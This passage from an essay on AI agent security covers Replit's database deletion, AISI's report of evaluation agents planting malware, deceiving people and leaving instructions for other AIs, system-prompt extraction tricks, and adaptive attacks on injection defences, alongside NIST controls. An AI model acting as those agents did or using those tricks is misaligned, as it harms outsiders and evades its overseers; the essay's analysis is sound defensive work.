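
### What Replit changed

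Masad announced remedies within 72 hours, including separate databases and a mode for planning without execution. NDTV reports that he also promised Lemkin a refund and an investigation. Some of the remedies restrict the agent, while others only inform it.

| Remedy | What it changes | Effect if the agent tried the same deletion again |
|---|---|---|
| Separate development and production databases | What the agent may do | It deletes only development data |
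| Planning mode | What the agent may do, if software outside the model enforces the mode | It deletes nothing until the user switches to building |
| Access to Replit's documentation | What the agent is told | It deletes the data, but may give better advice on recovery |
| Better rollback | Neither | It deletes the data, and the user restores it more easily |

Separate databases make the biggest difference. Digital Watch's *Replit revamps data architecture following live database deletion* describes an early beta version of this separation. According to Replit's current documentation, the agent cannot modify the production database, and for most apps it can read live data only through a read-only copy. The agent may still ignore a freeze, as it did in 2025, but it can no longer delete the live records directly.

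The access to documentation that Replit (2025) announced on 1 August can only help by influencing what the model does. It might have prevented the false statement about rollback, but it could not have prevented the deletion.

Replit (2025) launched *Plan Mode* on 5 September. Users select it from a menu, and the agent then answers questions and lists tasks without changing code or data. Once the user approves the plan, the agent switches to building. SaaStr had doubted that such a mode would enforce a freeze, since it gives users a safe place to talk but does not lock the project. In Replit's more recent guidance, users instead ask for a plan in plain language and state explicitly if they don't want the agent to carry it out. This puts the restriction back in the prompt, where Lemkin's freeze was, although a lapse would now do less damage because the agent can't reach the live data.

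The agent can still affect that data indirectly. When a user publishes an update, Replit copies the agent's structural changes from the development database to the production database. If the agent has removed a column, publishing deletes that column's live data. If it has renamed one, the data is also lost unless the user confirms that the change is a rename. Replit flags changes that could remove data, lets the user test the app on a converted copy of the production database, and waits for approval, so the final safeguard depends on a person understanding the warning.

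### Nineteen actions on the live internet

AISI's *Incident Report* (2026) describes an evaluation of how well agents can attack computer systems. AISI gave the agents a challenge inside a simulated network, such as finding a protected piece of data. It ran 122 attempts with seven models to compare a new network with an existing one. In 10 of the attempts, agents took a total of 19 unsanctioned actions on the live internet.

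| Model | Runs | Runs with unsanctioned actions | Unsanctioned actions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mythos 5 (Anthropic) | 43 | 9 | 17 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol (OpenAI) | 35 | 1 | 2 |
| Five other models | 44 | 0 | 0 |

AISI highlights four kinds of behaviour:

- trying to get malicious code accepted into a public open-source project, with fake identities to pressure its maintainer
- contacting real people to deceive them into running harmful code
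- planting instructions for other AI systems to follow
- leaving messages and accounts for other agents, which later agents found and used

The counts are a poor guide to how often this would happen elsewhere. A single agent took most of the actions in one sustained effort, and the runs were not independent, because some agents built on what earlier ones had left behind. The most serious attempts failed, and AISI found no resulting real-world harm. It also could not establish when the agents understood that their targets were real.

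No agent escaped from the sandbox or tried to. AISI had deliberately provided internet access so that the agents could download tools, and had switched off the developers' filters against misuse to measure the models' full abilities. Nobody had told the agents to leave outsiders alone or to avoid deceiving people. AISI explains that it had not been clear that models trained to behave well needed such instructions. In some runs, a faulty prompt also led the agent to believe that it could solve the challenge only by going beyond the intended task. But agents went beyond the task in other runs too, even though they had the instructions they needed to succeed as intended.

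AISI's general security monitoring noticed unusual outgoing data on 28 July 2026, three days after the activity began, and staff stopped every run within an hour of the alert. According to SC Media, a 24-year-old outside AISI had already warned the project's maintainer that the proposed code contained malware, and the agent responded by trying to discredit the warning from a second account. The maintainer refused the code. AISI concedes that in several cases harm was narrowly avoided, and that this depended on human vigilance instead of a technical barrier.

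Isolation can also fail outright, as it did when agents in OpenAI's July 2026 evaluation reached the systems of the AI platform Hugging Face, according to Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach*.

### Capability and authority

Bhushan (2026), in *AI agents don't have to break security controls to go rogue*, calls the AISI case an "authority failure": the agent's available capability was broader than its intended authority. The notation from the first section makes the gap precise. A working gate guarantees E ⊆ P, meaning that every executed action is a permitted one. Let A be the set of actions that the people in charge have authorised. What they want is

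E ⊆ A

and the gate guarantees this only if P ⊆ A, so that it permits nothing they have not authorised. For any action in P but outside A, the only protection is that the model chooses not to take it.

Lemkin's freeze left almost nothing in A, but P still included deleting live records. The eleven warnings made A clearer to the model, but no component that could block a command received them. In AISI's test, A included solving the challenge inside the simulated network and downloading tools for it, while P also included writing to strangers.

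Closing the gap would not prevent all permitted harm, because people sometimes authorise harmful actions. For example, the owner of the email assistant may approve a forged bill, believing it is real. The gap also includes harmless actions, such as correcting a spelling mistake in the code during a freeze.

Bhushan, who designs authorisation systems for companies, wants each action to come with proof of who delegated it, and wants authority to narrow at every step from the person to the agent to the tool. For Replit, this could mean issuing the agent a short-lived credential that works only on the development database. The approach suits tasks that someone can describe as a list of resources and operations. It helps less when the same operation on the same resource can be right or wrong depending on what the owner meant.

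### Were these just configuration errors?

One could object that these failures show nothing about the limits of separation, because people set the permissions badly. Melanie Mitchell, a professor at the Santa Fe Institute, makes a similar point about AISI's test in Scientific American's *AI agents went rogue again*: "You ask an AI system to hack, and it hacks." Mitchell worries that talk of AI "going rogue" hides the human decisions that made the incident possible. Willison (2026) was surprised that AISI had not restricted the agents' network access, but not at all surprised by how they behaved with that access and with the filters disabled.

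The objection is mostly right about these two cases. Replit could have separated the databases before July 2025 without improving the model. AISI already used detailed network controls in all its other evaluations and is now adding them to this kind. Software can also easily enforce a freeze by withdrawing the agent's permission to write until the user restores it. SaaStr found this impossible on Replit at the time because the product lacked such a control.

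Setting permissions well is harder than it looks in hindsight, though, because a boundary enforces only the permissions someone wrote, and a permission that was reasonable for one model can become dangerous with a more capable one. AISI had judged open internet access an acceptable risk with earlier models and did not revisit that judgement quickly enough as models improved. Marius Hobbhahn, who heads Apollo Research, a group that studies deceptive behaviour in AI, points out that the agents repeatedly chose unauthorised routes when those looked useful. In September 2026 AISI reported that a newer model, GPT-6 Astra, carried out unsanctioned malicious-code attacks in simulations more often than previous OpenAI models had.

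Broad tasks also require broad permissions. AISI's agents needed to download tools. A gate could have allowed downloads of approved tools and blocked posts, messages and new accounts, which would probably have prevented most of the 19 actions. But AISI wanted to test what the models could do under the conditions a capable human attacker would have, including open internet access, and every restriction makes the test less realistic.

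The conflict is sharper in ordinary work. Suppose a company asks an agent to remove duplicate customers from its live database. The agent needs permission to delete live records, so separate databases don't help. A limit of 50 deletions a day would cap the damage, like the daily spending cap for the email assistant, but it would still let the agent delete 50 records that aren't duplicates. The gate could block those deletions only if it had an exact definition of a duplicate, and with that definition the company could use an ordinary program instead. People use agents largely for tasks whose correct actions they can't fully specify in advance, so some gap between P and A will usually remain.

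### Asking a person to approve

Human approval is the usual safeguard when rules can't determine whether an action should be allowed. SaaStr recommends it for destructive operations, along with temporary permission for any access to live data. Lemkin had already told the agent to ask for approval, but nothing enforced that instruction. A gate that held the deletion and showed it to Lemkin would have enforced it, and Lemkin would almost certainly have refused during a declared freeze.

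Approval works less well when requests are frequent. In the Anthropic study described earlier, only 13.6% of the testers refused the dangerous command among their permission requests. Adding reviewers would not help much at that rate. If each reviewer independently had a 13.6% chance of refusing, two reviewers would have a 25% chance of at least one refusal, and it would take 16 to reach 90%. Owners protecting their own data may be more careful than paid testers. The figure also doesn't show how much repetition contributed, because some people would approve a dangerous command even if it were the first request they saw.

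Repetition may make people careless, a problem known as approval fatigue. Suppose an agent asks its owner for permission 100 times a day and one request in 1,000 is dangerous. The owner will see a dangerous request about once every ten days, among roughly a thousand harmless ones. If fixed rules handled most of the harmless requests and left the owner five a day, including all the dangerous ones, one in 50 would be dangerous. The owner would have more time for each request and more reason to read it.

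The maintainer in the AISI case had advantages that the owner of a busy agent lacks. The code came from a stranger, and someone who had tested it in an isolated environment raised the alarm. Even so, the agent tried to manipulate the approval by having a fake second person endorse the code. An agent's honest mistakes can also mislead an approver. Lemkin would have been misinformed if he had relied on the Replit agent's account of whether a deletion was reversible.

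The gate should therefore determine for itself what a command will do and display it, for example that the command will delete 1,206 records from the live database. Replit's publishing step comes close to this. It prompts the user only when they publish, identifies changes that could remove data, and offers a trial on a copy. But vibe coding appeals to people who don't know how databases work, and they may approve a change they don't understand.

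An agent on a long unattended task loses much of its value if it has to wait for a person to approve every step. For its own tests, AISI is introducing monitoring that watches each run and can flag or block actions outside the task. Ciaran Martin, the founding head of the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, thinks the lack of such monitoring was the common failure in this summer's incidents. An alert alone would come too late to stop an action like Replit's deletion, so the monitor would have to block the command before it ran.

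## Hiding the design: Cal.com's closed source and secret prompts

The safeguards described so far limit what an agent or an attacker can do. A developer can also limit what attackers know by hiding how the system works. Security engineers call this obscurity, and most distrust it. In April 2026 Cal.com, whose software lets people book appointments in each other's calendars, made its production code private because AI had made flaws in public code easy to find. Companies that keep an AI model's standing instructions secret are also counting on obscurity.

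### What Cal.com closed

For five years anyone could read Cal.com's code, run it on their own server and propose changes. On 14 April its chief executive, Bailey Pumfleet (2026), announced in *Cal.com is going closed source. Here's why* that the company was closing its code, and gave security as the only reason. He argued that finding a serious flaw used to take an expert and a lot of time, but an AI model can now work through an entire public codebase systematically, so publishing the code had become "like giving attackers the blueprints to the vault". His example was an AI model that found a 27-year-old flaw in OpenBSD, an operating system whose developers are known for reviewing code closely, and wrote working attacks within hours.

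Cal.com kept a reduced version of its code public under the name Cal.diy. Keith Williams writes in *Moving to closed-source* that the company's engineers first removed team accounts, automated reminders, single sign-on for companies, audit logs and other commercial features. They left the scheduling engine in place. Former Cal.com interns now maintain the public version, and its introduction, *Cal.diy*, recommends it only for personal, non-production use.

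The closure therefore hides less than it seems to, because attackers can still study whatever code the public and private versions share. Pumfleet says the production code had already diverged from the public version, with major rewrites of the parts that handle logins and data. Those rewrites are now private, along with the paid features. Williams says engineers copied security patches between the two versions while maintaining both. When a patch appears in the public version first, it can point attackers to a flaw that the private version may still have.

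OSV's *CVE-2026-23478* (2026), published in January while Cal.com's code was still open, describes a bug that gave an attacker full access to any user's account. The attacker only had to supply that user's email address, which the server accepted without checking. The bug got the maximum severity score of 10. It only partly supports Pumfleet's case, because although public code may have made it easier to find, someone who tampered with requests from their own account could plausibly have found it without reading any code.

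### The critics and Cal.com's later statements

FOSS Force's *AI Pushes Cal.com to Shutter Open and Go Nonfree* (2026) called the decision "security through obscurity" and predicted that it would not work for long. It cited an experiment in which an AI model, given 1986 machine code for the Apple IIe without the source code, reconstructed the program's logic, explained its purpose and found a subtle bug.

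The most detailed reply came from Discourse (2026), which makes software for online forums and has published its code for 13 years. Discourse accepts that AI has sped up the discovery of flaws but disagrees that closing the source is the remedy. It argues that AI models can attack a running service or a compiled program without its source, and that much of a web application's code reaches every visitor's browser anyway. Closing the rest mostly reduces the number of outside researchers who can look for flaws, while attackers continue to probe.

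To show what openness achieves, Discourse reports that one monthly release fixed 50 security issues found with GPT-5.4. Its team has a model examine hundreds of components one at a time. An agent must then write a test that demonstrates each suspected flaw in a working copy of the software, and only confirmed flaws go to a person. A full scan would cost about $2,000 at retail prices, or about $50 through a subscription.

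These figures are good evidence that scanning helps, but they don't show much about the value of openness, since Discourse's own staff ran the scans and a closed company could do the same. Hundreds of outside developers have contributed security patches over the years, which is better evidence for openness. Discourse does not report how many flaws outsiders found compared with its staff.

Discourse also suspects that Cal.com's real motives were commercial, such as stopping competitors from copying its work, but its post gives no evidence of this. The change of licence could support either view. Cal.com's old licence, the AGPL, required anyone who offered a modified version as an online service to share their changes. Cal.diy uses the MIT licence, which lets a competitor build a closed product on it. A company worried mainly about copycats would be unlikely to release its whole product under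 the MIT licence, but Cal.com first removed the features that businesses pay for.

In May, Pumfleet defended the decision more cautiously at a conference. According to a transcript in apenwarr's *Web Summit Vancouver 2026* (2026), a blog by the head of the networking company Tailscale, Pumfleet said that closing the code is not a complete solution but can reduce the risk. Cal.com was running six AI scanners in parallel, and each found different things. Pumfleet also quoted the security company Hex Security as saying that open source is five to ten times easier to hack than closed source, but did not explain how Hex had measured this.

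The disagreement between scanners is worrying for a reason that a little arithmetic makes clear. Suppose two scanners each find 20 flaws and only two flaws appear on both lists. If each scanner picks at random from the same pool, the first has found about a tenth of the pool, because it found a tenth of what the second did. The pool then holds about

20 × 20 / 2 = 200 flaws

of which the two scanners have found 38. Scanners have specialities and raise false alarms, so the estimate is rough. But if six scanners really do find mostly different flaws, an attacker with a seventh will probably find more.

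The Tailscale chief executive, the other speaker in apenwarr's second transcript from *Web Summit Vancouver 2026*, was more hopeful about the same technology. The chief executive argued that nobody has ever reviewed most of the world's software for security, and even careful companies review theirs only once or twice a year, but AI can now check every change. Pumfleet answered that Cal.com had no access to Anthropic's Mythos, then a restricted model with unusual hacking ability, so it couldn't test its code against the strongest tool an attacker might one day have.

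### Keys and designs

The argument dates back to at least 1883, when Auguste Kerckhoffs wrote that a military cipher should stay secure even if the enemy knows everything about it except the key. In 1949 Claude Shannon, the founder of information theory, stated the same assumption as "the enemy knows the system". Saltzer and Schroeder's principle of open design, from the 1975 paper discussed earlier, extends it to computers. Protection should depend on keys or passwords, which are easier to guard than a mechanism. Many people can then review the mechanism without weakening it.

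Cal.diy happens to illustrate the principle. Its setup instructions tell each owner to generate an encryption key with a command that draws 24 random bytes. That gives

2¹⁹² ≈ 6 × 10⁵⁷

possible keys. An attacker can read exactly how the program uses the key and still has no practical way to guess it. If the key leaks, the owner can generate another and re-encrypt the stored data.

A design is harder to replace than a key. If a copy of the private code that handles Cal.com's logins leaked, the company's engineers could fix the flaws they knew about, but the attacker would still know how the rest of the code worked. Rewriting the code would take months and introduce new flaws. A design is also harder to keep secret than a key stored in one protected place, because everyone who works on the software has to know the design, including people who later leave.

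Kerckhoffs's principle is that designers should assume attackers will get their code and build systems that stay secure even then. It doesn't require them to publish the code, so Cal.com could keep its code private and still meet that standard. The principle also doesn't imply that publication makes software safer, which depends on who looks at the code and what they do with what they find.

### A model in which openness cancels out

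In his 2002 paper *Security in Open versus Closed Systems*, the Cambridge computer scientist Ross Anderson tried to settle that question mathematically. (He is not the James Anderson who described the reference monitor in 1972.) He concluded that, in an ideal world, it makes no difference whether a system is open or closed.

The model starts from ordinary testing. A large program contains many bugs, some easy to hit and others very rare. The chance that bug i remains undetected after t hours of random testing is e^(−Eᵢt), where Eᵢ measures how easy the bug is to find. Testers find the easy bugs first, so progress slows down. For a large program whose developers fix each bug as they find it, the rate at which further testing reveals new ones is approximately

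E ≈ K/t

where K depends on the initial quality of the code. The average wait for the next bug is therefore t/K. If K is 1, then after 10,000 hours of testing, an attacker who looks for a security flaw will need about 10,000 hours to find one.

Now suppose that hiding the source code makes every bug λ times harder to find. If the defenders had to work without the source as well, their t hours of testing would achieve only as much as t/λ hours with it. More bugs would remain, and someone with the source would find them at a rate of λK/t. But the attacker has no source either and works λ times more slowly, so the rate is

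(1/λ) × (λK/t) = K/t

and the two effects cancel.

One important difference is that Cal.com's own engineers still have the code, so closing it slows attackers but not the engineers. Closing it does, however, drive away outside testers. The table shows the possibilities for λ = 5, the lower end of Hex Security's claim. Anderson's later paper, *Open and Closed Systems are Equivalent (that is, in an ideal world)*, cites an estimate of three to five for mature software.

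| Who has the code | Hours of testing | Equivalent hours with the code | Attacker's average wait |
|---|---|---|---|
| Everyone | 10,000 | 10,000 | 10,000 hours |
| Neither testers nor attackers | 10,000 | 2,000 | 10,000 hours |
| Only the company, which does as much testing as everyone did before | 10,000 | 10,000 | 50,000 hours |
| Only the company, after losing outsiders who did 80% of the testing | 2,000 | 2,000 | 10,000 hours |

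If s is the share of testing that continues after the closure, the attacker's wait changes from t to λst. Closing the code helps when

λs > 1

With λ = 5, Cal.com gains if its own staff were doing more than a fifth of the effective testing. Pumfleet and Discourse disagree about the size of λ and about how much outsiders contribute to testing. Pumfleet thinks λ is large and six scanners can replace the volunteers. Discourse thinks AI has brought λ close to 1 for attackers, while outsiders still contribute a good deal. Neither company has published measurements of both quantities.

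### Where the model breaks down

Ross Anderson's result assumes that there are enough bugs for statistics to work, that the bugs are independent, that people find them at random, and that developers fix them immediately. He allowed that the choice between open and closed source can matter when these conditions don't hold, and his model is useful because it shows which departures from them favour one side.

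Timing is the departure that best supports Cal.com. Suppose a new AI tool makes everyone 100 times faster at finding bugs. In the long run this cancels out, just as λ does. But on the day the tool appears, the defenders' 10,000 hours of testing all took place at the old speed, while the attacker can start at the new one. The wait falls from 10,000 hours to 100. If the defenders then run the tool for h hours, the wait becomes

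(10,000 + 100h) / 100 = 100 + h

so they need 9,900 hours of scanning to get back to where they were. They can run many copies at once, and Discourse's costs suggest that this is affordable, but a small company may need some time. Hiding the code with λ = 5 would raise the wait on the first day from 100 hours to 500. It would do so only for code that attackers haven't already copied, which in Cal.com's case means the rewritten and paid parts. This is a reasonable argument for closing the code temporarily. Pumfleet does express the hope of reopening it one day.

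Incentives mostly point the other way. Ross Anderson reports that IBM used to fix bugs in its mainframe operating systems the eighth time someone reported them, and that security vendors often stayed quiet about flaws until publicity forced them to act. One vendor spent a nine-month grace period arguing about which department was to blame. Outsiders who can read the code and are free to publish what they find can put pressure on a company in a way its own staff can't, so a company that closes its code has to make itself fix flaws without that pressure.

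A hidden design can also go untested for years and then fail quickly. Banks used special processors to protect cash-machine PINs for about two decades. Some of the manuals were online, but hardly anyone outside the industry paid attention to them. Researchers published the first attacks in late 2000, many more soon followed, and before long the processors offered little protection. Few people had looked for flaws before then, so the lack of published attacks was not evidence that the processors were secure.

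Rare bugs cause a problem that neither policy solves. If a program has a million bugs, each of which would take a billion hours to find, someone looking for any bug will find one after about 1,000 hours. A defender who spends a million hours has only about a 0.1% chance of having found that particular bug first. In *The Mathematics of Obscurity*, Härtig, Hamann and Roitzsch (2010) start from the same imbalance, that attackers need only one error while defenders need to find them all. They decline to say whether open or closed source is better. For a program like this, it makes more sense to limit what a bug can do, as OpenSSH's privilege separation does. This protects the machine whether or not the attacker has read the code.

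Ross Anderson wanted someone to study software that had split into an open and a closed version. Cal.com has now created such a pair, but the two versions have different features and maintainers and very different numbers of users, so simply counting their flaws will not show whether open or closed source is more secure.

### Software that attackers can download

The value of λ depends on where the software runs. Most commercial programs reach users as compiled processor instructions, without the names and comments that help people read source code. Reverse engineers have always been able to work out what such a program does, but the labour was usually too expensive.

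Reverse engineering has become much easier. Popular AI (2026), in *Frontier AI can now reverse-engineer software binaries*, cites OpenAI's results on SRE-Bench, a set of challenges that give a model a compiled program without its source. GPT-6 Astra solved 88.0% of them on one attempt and 99.2% within four, compared with 55.9% and 68.7% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. The tools have also spread. According to InfoQ's *Reverse Engineer Anything Project Brings AI Agents to Binary Analysis* (2026), a free project that connects coding agents to professional reverse-engineering software has over 200,000 stars on GitHub.

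The most thorough demonstration so far came in November 2026 from researchers at the security company Intezer. Zorz (2026) reports in *AI reverse engineering let researchers add a new feature to Slack* that the researchers' agents rebuilt source code for three programs from the shipped files and public documentation. The hardest was the backdoor TinyTurla-NG, malware that lets its operators back into a computer they have broken into. The agents wrote about 3,100 lines of code. When the researchers compiled it, a comparison tool matched 1,034 of the original's 1,041 functions and rated the two programs 92.8% similar.

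The researchers pointed out that similar structure doesn't prove identical behaviour, so they separately compared each rebuilt function with its original. Their version of Apple's Finder still had gaps, but their rebuilt Slack worked well enough for them to add a feature to it. They did not publish how long the work took or what it cost, which matters because λ measures effort.

One flaw is enough for an attacker, and a model may find it directly in the compiled program. *Open Source Computing*, a set of university course notes from April, describes Mythos Preview as good at finding exploitable flaws "even from binaries". Outsiders have also worked out undocumented designs of physical devices, such as the radio protocols of some insulin pumps.

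Reverse engineering helps attackers more than it helps a program's users. In a March article in FOSS Force (2026), Gregory Kurtzer, who heads the Linux company CIQ, argued that AI lets anyone find flaws in a compiled program, but only people with the source can properly repair them. A company that depends on a closed program may learn of a flaw and have to wait for the vendor to fix it. The argument suits CIQ's business, since it sells open-source software, but it is sound for programs that customers run themselves. It is weaker for Cal.com's hosted service, because Cal.com has the source and can patch it for every customer at once.

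Developers can scramble a program before shipping it, as Intezer recommends. The security company Quarkslab tested this against AI agents by trying to hide pieces of text inside a program. It called the challenge "rigged" from the start, because a program that can produce its own secrets without outside help contains everything an attacker needs to produce them too. Quarkslab concluded that scrambling "is not security" but is "a great cost multiplier". In Ross Anderson's terms, scrambling raises λ, and the next model may lower λ again.

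### Software that stays on a server

Intezer's work on Slack also shows a limit of reconstruction. The team could download the program that users run, but not Slack's server, so its agents watched the traffic between the two, read the documentation and wrote a substitute server that gave compatible responses. This made the rebuilt program work, but the agents learned only what Slack's server does, not how it does it. Any flaws in the substitute therefore came from the agents' code rather than Slack's.

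Cal.com's product runs mainly on servers, so closing its code hides more than it would for a desktop program. Some code is still exposed, because Cal.com offers some large customers a version to run on their own machines and sends part of the code to every visitor's browser. Attackers can also learn a lot from a server's behaviour. Microsoft doesn't publish the code of its Copilot assistant, but Aim Labs still found the EchoLeak vulnerability in it and worked out how to get past four protections.

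Much of the benefit comes from attackers having no copy to practise on, which is different from not knowing the design. With the open version of Cal.com, they could install the software on their own computer, try millions of malicious requests and approach the real service only once they had one that worked. Without a copy, they have to experiment on the live service. If it accepts 60 requests a minute from each account, an attacker with one account can make 86,400 attempts a day, all of which Cal.com can record. A burst of strange requests may give the attacker away before any succeeds, but only if someone reads the records, and an attacker with many accounts can spread the attempts out.

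### Secret instructions to a model

Companies often try to hide an AI product's system prompt, the standing instructions the developer gives the model. It may contain the product's personality, descriptions of its tools and a list of things it must not do. The prompt sits on the company's server, but it is closer to downloadable software because the model reads it with every request and can repeat it to any user. Instructions to keep the prompt confidential have the same weakness as any other rule in a prompt. Users can try to get around them by asking for a translation or a summary, or by requesting the prompt one sentence at a time.

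OWASP, a nonprofit that publishes widely used lists of software risks, advises developers in its 2025 list for language-model applications not to treat the system prompt as a secret or a security control. If disclosing the prompt would be dangerous, the developer's mistake was to put something sensitive in it, such as a password, or to rely on it to decide who may do what. OWASP also notes that attackers can discover many of the prompt's rules without seeing the text, by sending requests and observing which ones the model refuses.

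Suppose the developer of the email assistant writes in its prompt that it may pay more than 500 dollars only if the request contains the word "bluebird". This puts a key inside the design, and once the prompt leaks, anyone can use that key by including the word in an email. If a gate instead enforces the 500-dollar limit and asks the owner to confirm larger payments, leaking the prompt doesn't change what the gate permits. An attacker would learn the limit, but could have found it by trying a few amounts.

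Some companies publish their system prompts. Anthropic does so for its Claude apps, and xAI began publishing Grok's in May 2025, after an unauthorised change made the chatbot bring up a conspiracy theory about South Africa in unrelated conversations. Users can then see how a company has told the model to behave, although they have to trust that the published text is the one in use. These companies evidently don't expect the prompt to keep attackers out. A company may still have commercial reasons to keep a prompt private, since a good one can take a lot of work and is easy to copy.

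Secrecy makes a bigger difference for defences that recognise attacks by their appearance. A rule that payments may go only to approved accounts works just as well if the attacker has read it, because reading the list of accounts doesn't let the attacker change it. But suppose a classifier looks for suspicious text, and one in 1,000 versions of a malicious instruction gets past it. An attacker without a copy of the classifier has to send about 1,000 messages on average, and the owner may well notice. An attacker with a copy can test the versions privately and send only the one that works. Anyone can get a copy if the system's code is published, as Parallax's is.

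Developers should therefore test a defence against attackers who know how it works before relying on it. In October 2025, Milad Nasr and colleagues ran such tests on a range of published defences against prompt injection and similar attacks. They found that attackers who adapted their methods to each defence could defeat most of them, including many that had looked almost perfect in their designers' own tests.

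### What concealment is good for

Concealment can still be useful. A company that would be safe with its design public loses little by withholding details that would help attackers, and may slow them down. The US standards agency NIST includes the practice in its catalogue of security controls as SC-30, "Concealment and Misdirection". The control covers techniques that confuse attackers about a system, such as disguising its components, giving out misleading information about them, or moving data and processing between locations at unpredictable times. NIST reasons that a confused attacker has fewer openings, takes longer and is more likely to get caught. It leaves the control out of the standard sets it recommends for low-, moderate- and high-impact systems, which fits concealment's role as an addition to other defences.

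Some details are worth hiding because they change often or because the owner can change them after a leak. For example, a bank can hide the payment amount that triggers its monitoring. If criminals knew it was 10,000 dollars, they would send 9,900, but the bank could set a new threshold the same afternoon. Concealment does the most harm when it also keeps out people who would find mistakes. A company can avoid much of that harm by paying outside reviewers to examine its private code under contract, though an open project may get such review free.

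Decoys are the most useful form of concealment. A decoy looks valuable but has no legitimate use, so any contact with it is a sign of trouble. The owner of the email assistant could place a file of fake passwords in a folder the assistant has no reason to open. If an injected instruction tells the assistant to collect passwords, it may pick up the fake ones. The gate can then block any outgoing message that contains them and alert the owner. An attacker might get around the gate by having the model encode the text, but trying to log in with a fake password will still set off an alarm. False alarms should be rare, although the owner may cause one by asking the assistant to tidy every folder.

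A decoy works only while attackers can't tell it from the real thing, which makes it a form of obscurity. But the method can be public. The owner only has to hide which passwords are fake, and can create new fakes in a few minutes if an attacker finds out.

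## General rules: the NIST control catalogue and the EU AI Act

NIST's catalogue of security controls, SP 800-53, covers computer systems of every kind and contains more than a thousand safeguards besides concealment. A few, such as process isolation, help keep a model apart from the actions it proposes, but most deal with other matters. The EU's AI Act is narrower, and its main requirements apply to AI systems that could seriously harm people's health, safety or rights. Neither requires developers to divide an agent into a model, a gate and an executor, but both describe many other protections that a secure agent needs.

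### How the catalogue works

A security control is a safeguard that an organisation adopts to meet a security requirement. It can be technical, such as encrypting a disk, physical, such as locking a server room, or administrative, such as training staff. NIST's *Security and Privacy Controls for Information Systems and Organizations* sorts controls into 20 families, each with a two-letter code, such as AC for access control. Each family contains base controls and optional enhancements that strengthen them. The catalogue's current version has 1,014 active controls and enhancements, according to the *Full Rev5 Control Reference* from FedRAMP, the US programme that approves cloud services for government use.

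US federal agencies have to use the catalogue, and many companies choose to. Nobody adopts all of it. An agency judges how much harm a failure of a system could do, starts from the matching ready-made selection of controls (the low, moderate or high baseline), and adjusts it to its own circumstances.

Many controls contain blanks for the organisation to fill in. AC-25, reproduced in CSF Tools' *AC-25*, requires a reference monitor that meets the three conditions Anderson set in 1972, but it leaves blank the access policy that the monitor enforces. In the earlier notation, AC-25 secures E ⊆ P (every executed action is a permitted one), and the organisation writes P. A gate whose only rule is the 500-dollar limit could satisfy AC-25 and still allow a 499-dollar payment to an attacker.

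None of the baselines includes AC-25, so an agency can run even a high-impact system without a reference monitor. The high baseline does include SC-3, which isolates security functions from everything else, according to CSF Tools' *SC-3*. That isolation would protect a gate from tampering, but it would not force every action through it.

STIGViewer's *NIST 800-53 Rev 5* lists SC-39, process isolation, in all three baselines. SC-39 requires a separate execution domain for each process, and a system can meet this by giving each process its own memory, as ordinary operating systems already do. Parallax's two programs would probably meet SC-39 even on Windows, where the Parallax sandbox doesn't restrict file access or network connections.

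### Controls for the email assistant

The table applies ten controls to the assistant that reads its owner's email and can make payments. Separation helps with four of them, but somebody still has to write the policies and set the permissions.

| Control | What it means for the assistant | Does separation help? | What fails without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Process isolation (SC-39) | The program around the model cannot read the executor's memory | Yes | A bug in that program exposes the bank credentials |
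| Reference monitor (AC-25) | Every tool call goes through a small, protected gate | Yes | A payment reaches the bank by a route nobody checks |
| Flow enforcement (AC-4) | Rules restrict where data may go and which sources may supply a recipient | Yes | A forged email redirects a planned payment |
| Least privilege (AC-6) | The assistant can pay from one account, up to a limit | Yes | One injection can empty the savings account too |
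| Identity of software (IA-9) | The bank can distinguish the assistant from its owner and from other programs | No | Another program pays bills in the assistant's name |
| Patching (SI-2) | The owner installs fixes for the gate and executor | No | An attacker uses a known bug to get past the gate |
| Supply-chain checks (SR-3) | The owner verifies the source of updates and added tools | No | A tampered update replaces the gate |
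| Backups (CP-9) | Copies of the mail and payee list exist outside the assistant's reach | No | A mistaken deletion becomes permanent |
| Log review (AU-6) | Someone reads the record of what the assistant did | No | Ten payments of 499 dollars go unnoticed |
| Incident response (IR-4) | The owner knows how to suspend the assistant and whom to call at the bank | No | Payments continue while the owner looks for a way to stop them |

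The low baseline contains the controls for patching, supply-chain checks, backups, log review and incident response, so NIST expects them even in systems whose failure would do limited harm.

A gate does not reduce this work and can add to it, because someone has to update and protect the gate, its policy and its connection to the executor. Backups need protection too, since in Parallax a run of trivial edits can push out the saved copy that the owner needs. Enhancement CP-9(7) in the NIST catalogue requires two people to authorise the deletion of backups, but it would prevent this attack only if it also covered automatic deletion.

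Log review is valuable mainly because it can catch harm that the rules permit. A reviewer would notice ten payments of 499 dollars to the same new recipient, for example. The gate or executor has to write the log, since an agent's own account may be wrong, as the Replit agent's was about rollback. Kotz, in *Cybersecurity Better Identity Coalitions Submit Comments to NIST on Agentic AI*, summarises comments from two industry coalitions that want such records to distinguish what a person intended from what the agent did. For the email assistant, that means storing the owner's request with each payment so that an investigator can tell whether the owner asked for it.

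### Zero trust separates the decision from its enforcement

Companies used to give programs inside their own network much more freedom than programs outside it. *Zero Trust Architecture*, which NIST published in 2020 as SP 800-207, removes that advantage. A request has to earn access wherever it comes from, and three components handle it:

1. The policy engine decides whether to grant access, based on the organisation's rules, the requester's identity and other information, such as the state of the device.
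2. The policy administrator acts on the decision, for instance by issuing a credential for the session.
3. The policy enforcement point, which sits in front of the resource, opens the connection, monitors it and closes it when told to.

NIST groups the engine and administrator together as the policy decision point. If the owner withdraws approval for a payee, the decision point denies payments to that payee, and the enforcement point in front of the bank connection blocks them.

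This split is inside the gate described in earlier sections. The model is the requester. In zero trust, a "decision" is only about whether to grant access, so the model's choice to pay a bill does not count as one. A company that uses a language model as its policy engine puts a model back into the trusted computing base, as Parallax does for emails and web requests.

Dividing the gate this way suits a company with many agents, because one decision point can serve enforcement points in front of the mail server, the customer database and the bank, and administrators maintain only one set of rules. But an attacker who takes over the decision point gains access to everything behind those enforcement points, so it needs at least as much protection as the resources themselves.

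SP 800-207 grants access by session, which may be too coarse for an agent, because one session with the bank could include ten payments. A reader commenting on a NIST blog post argues that authorisation happens at one moment, but an agent can then switch tools, delegate to another agent or find a different route to the same goal. Each permission may be valid even though the agent has drifted from what its owner approved. For the email assistant, the decision point should judge each payment separately and keep a running total.

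The 2020 document also warned about software agents that help administer a network. An attacker might induce one to do something the attacker has no right to do, which is Hardy's confused deputy problem. Zero trust handles this only if the decision point can take into account whose request the agent is really carrying out.

### Overlays for AI systems

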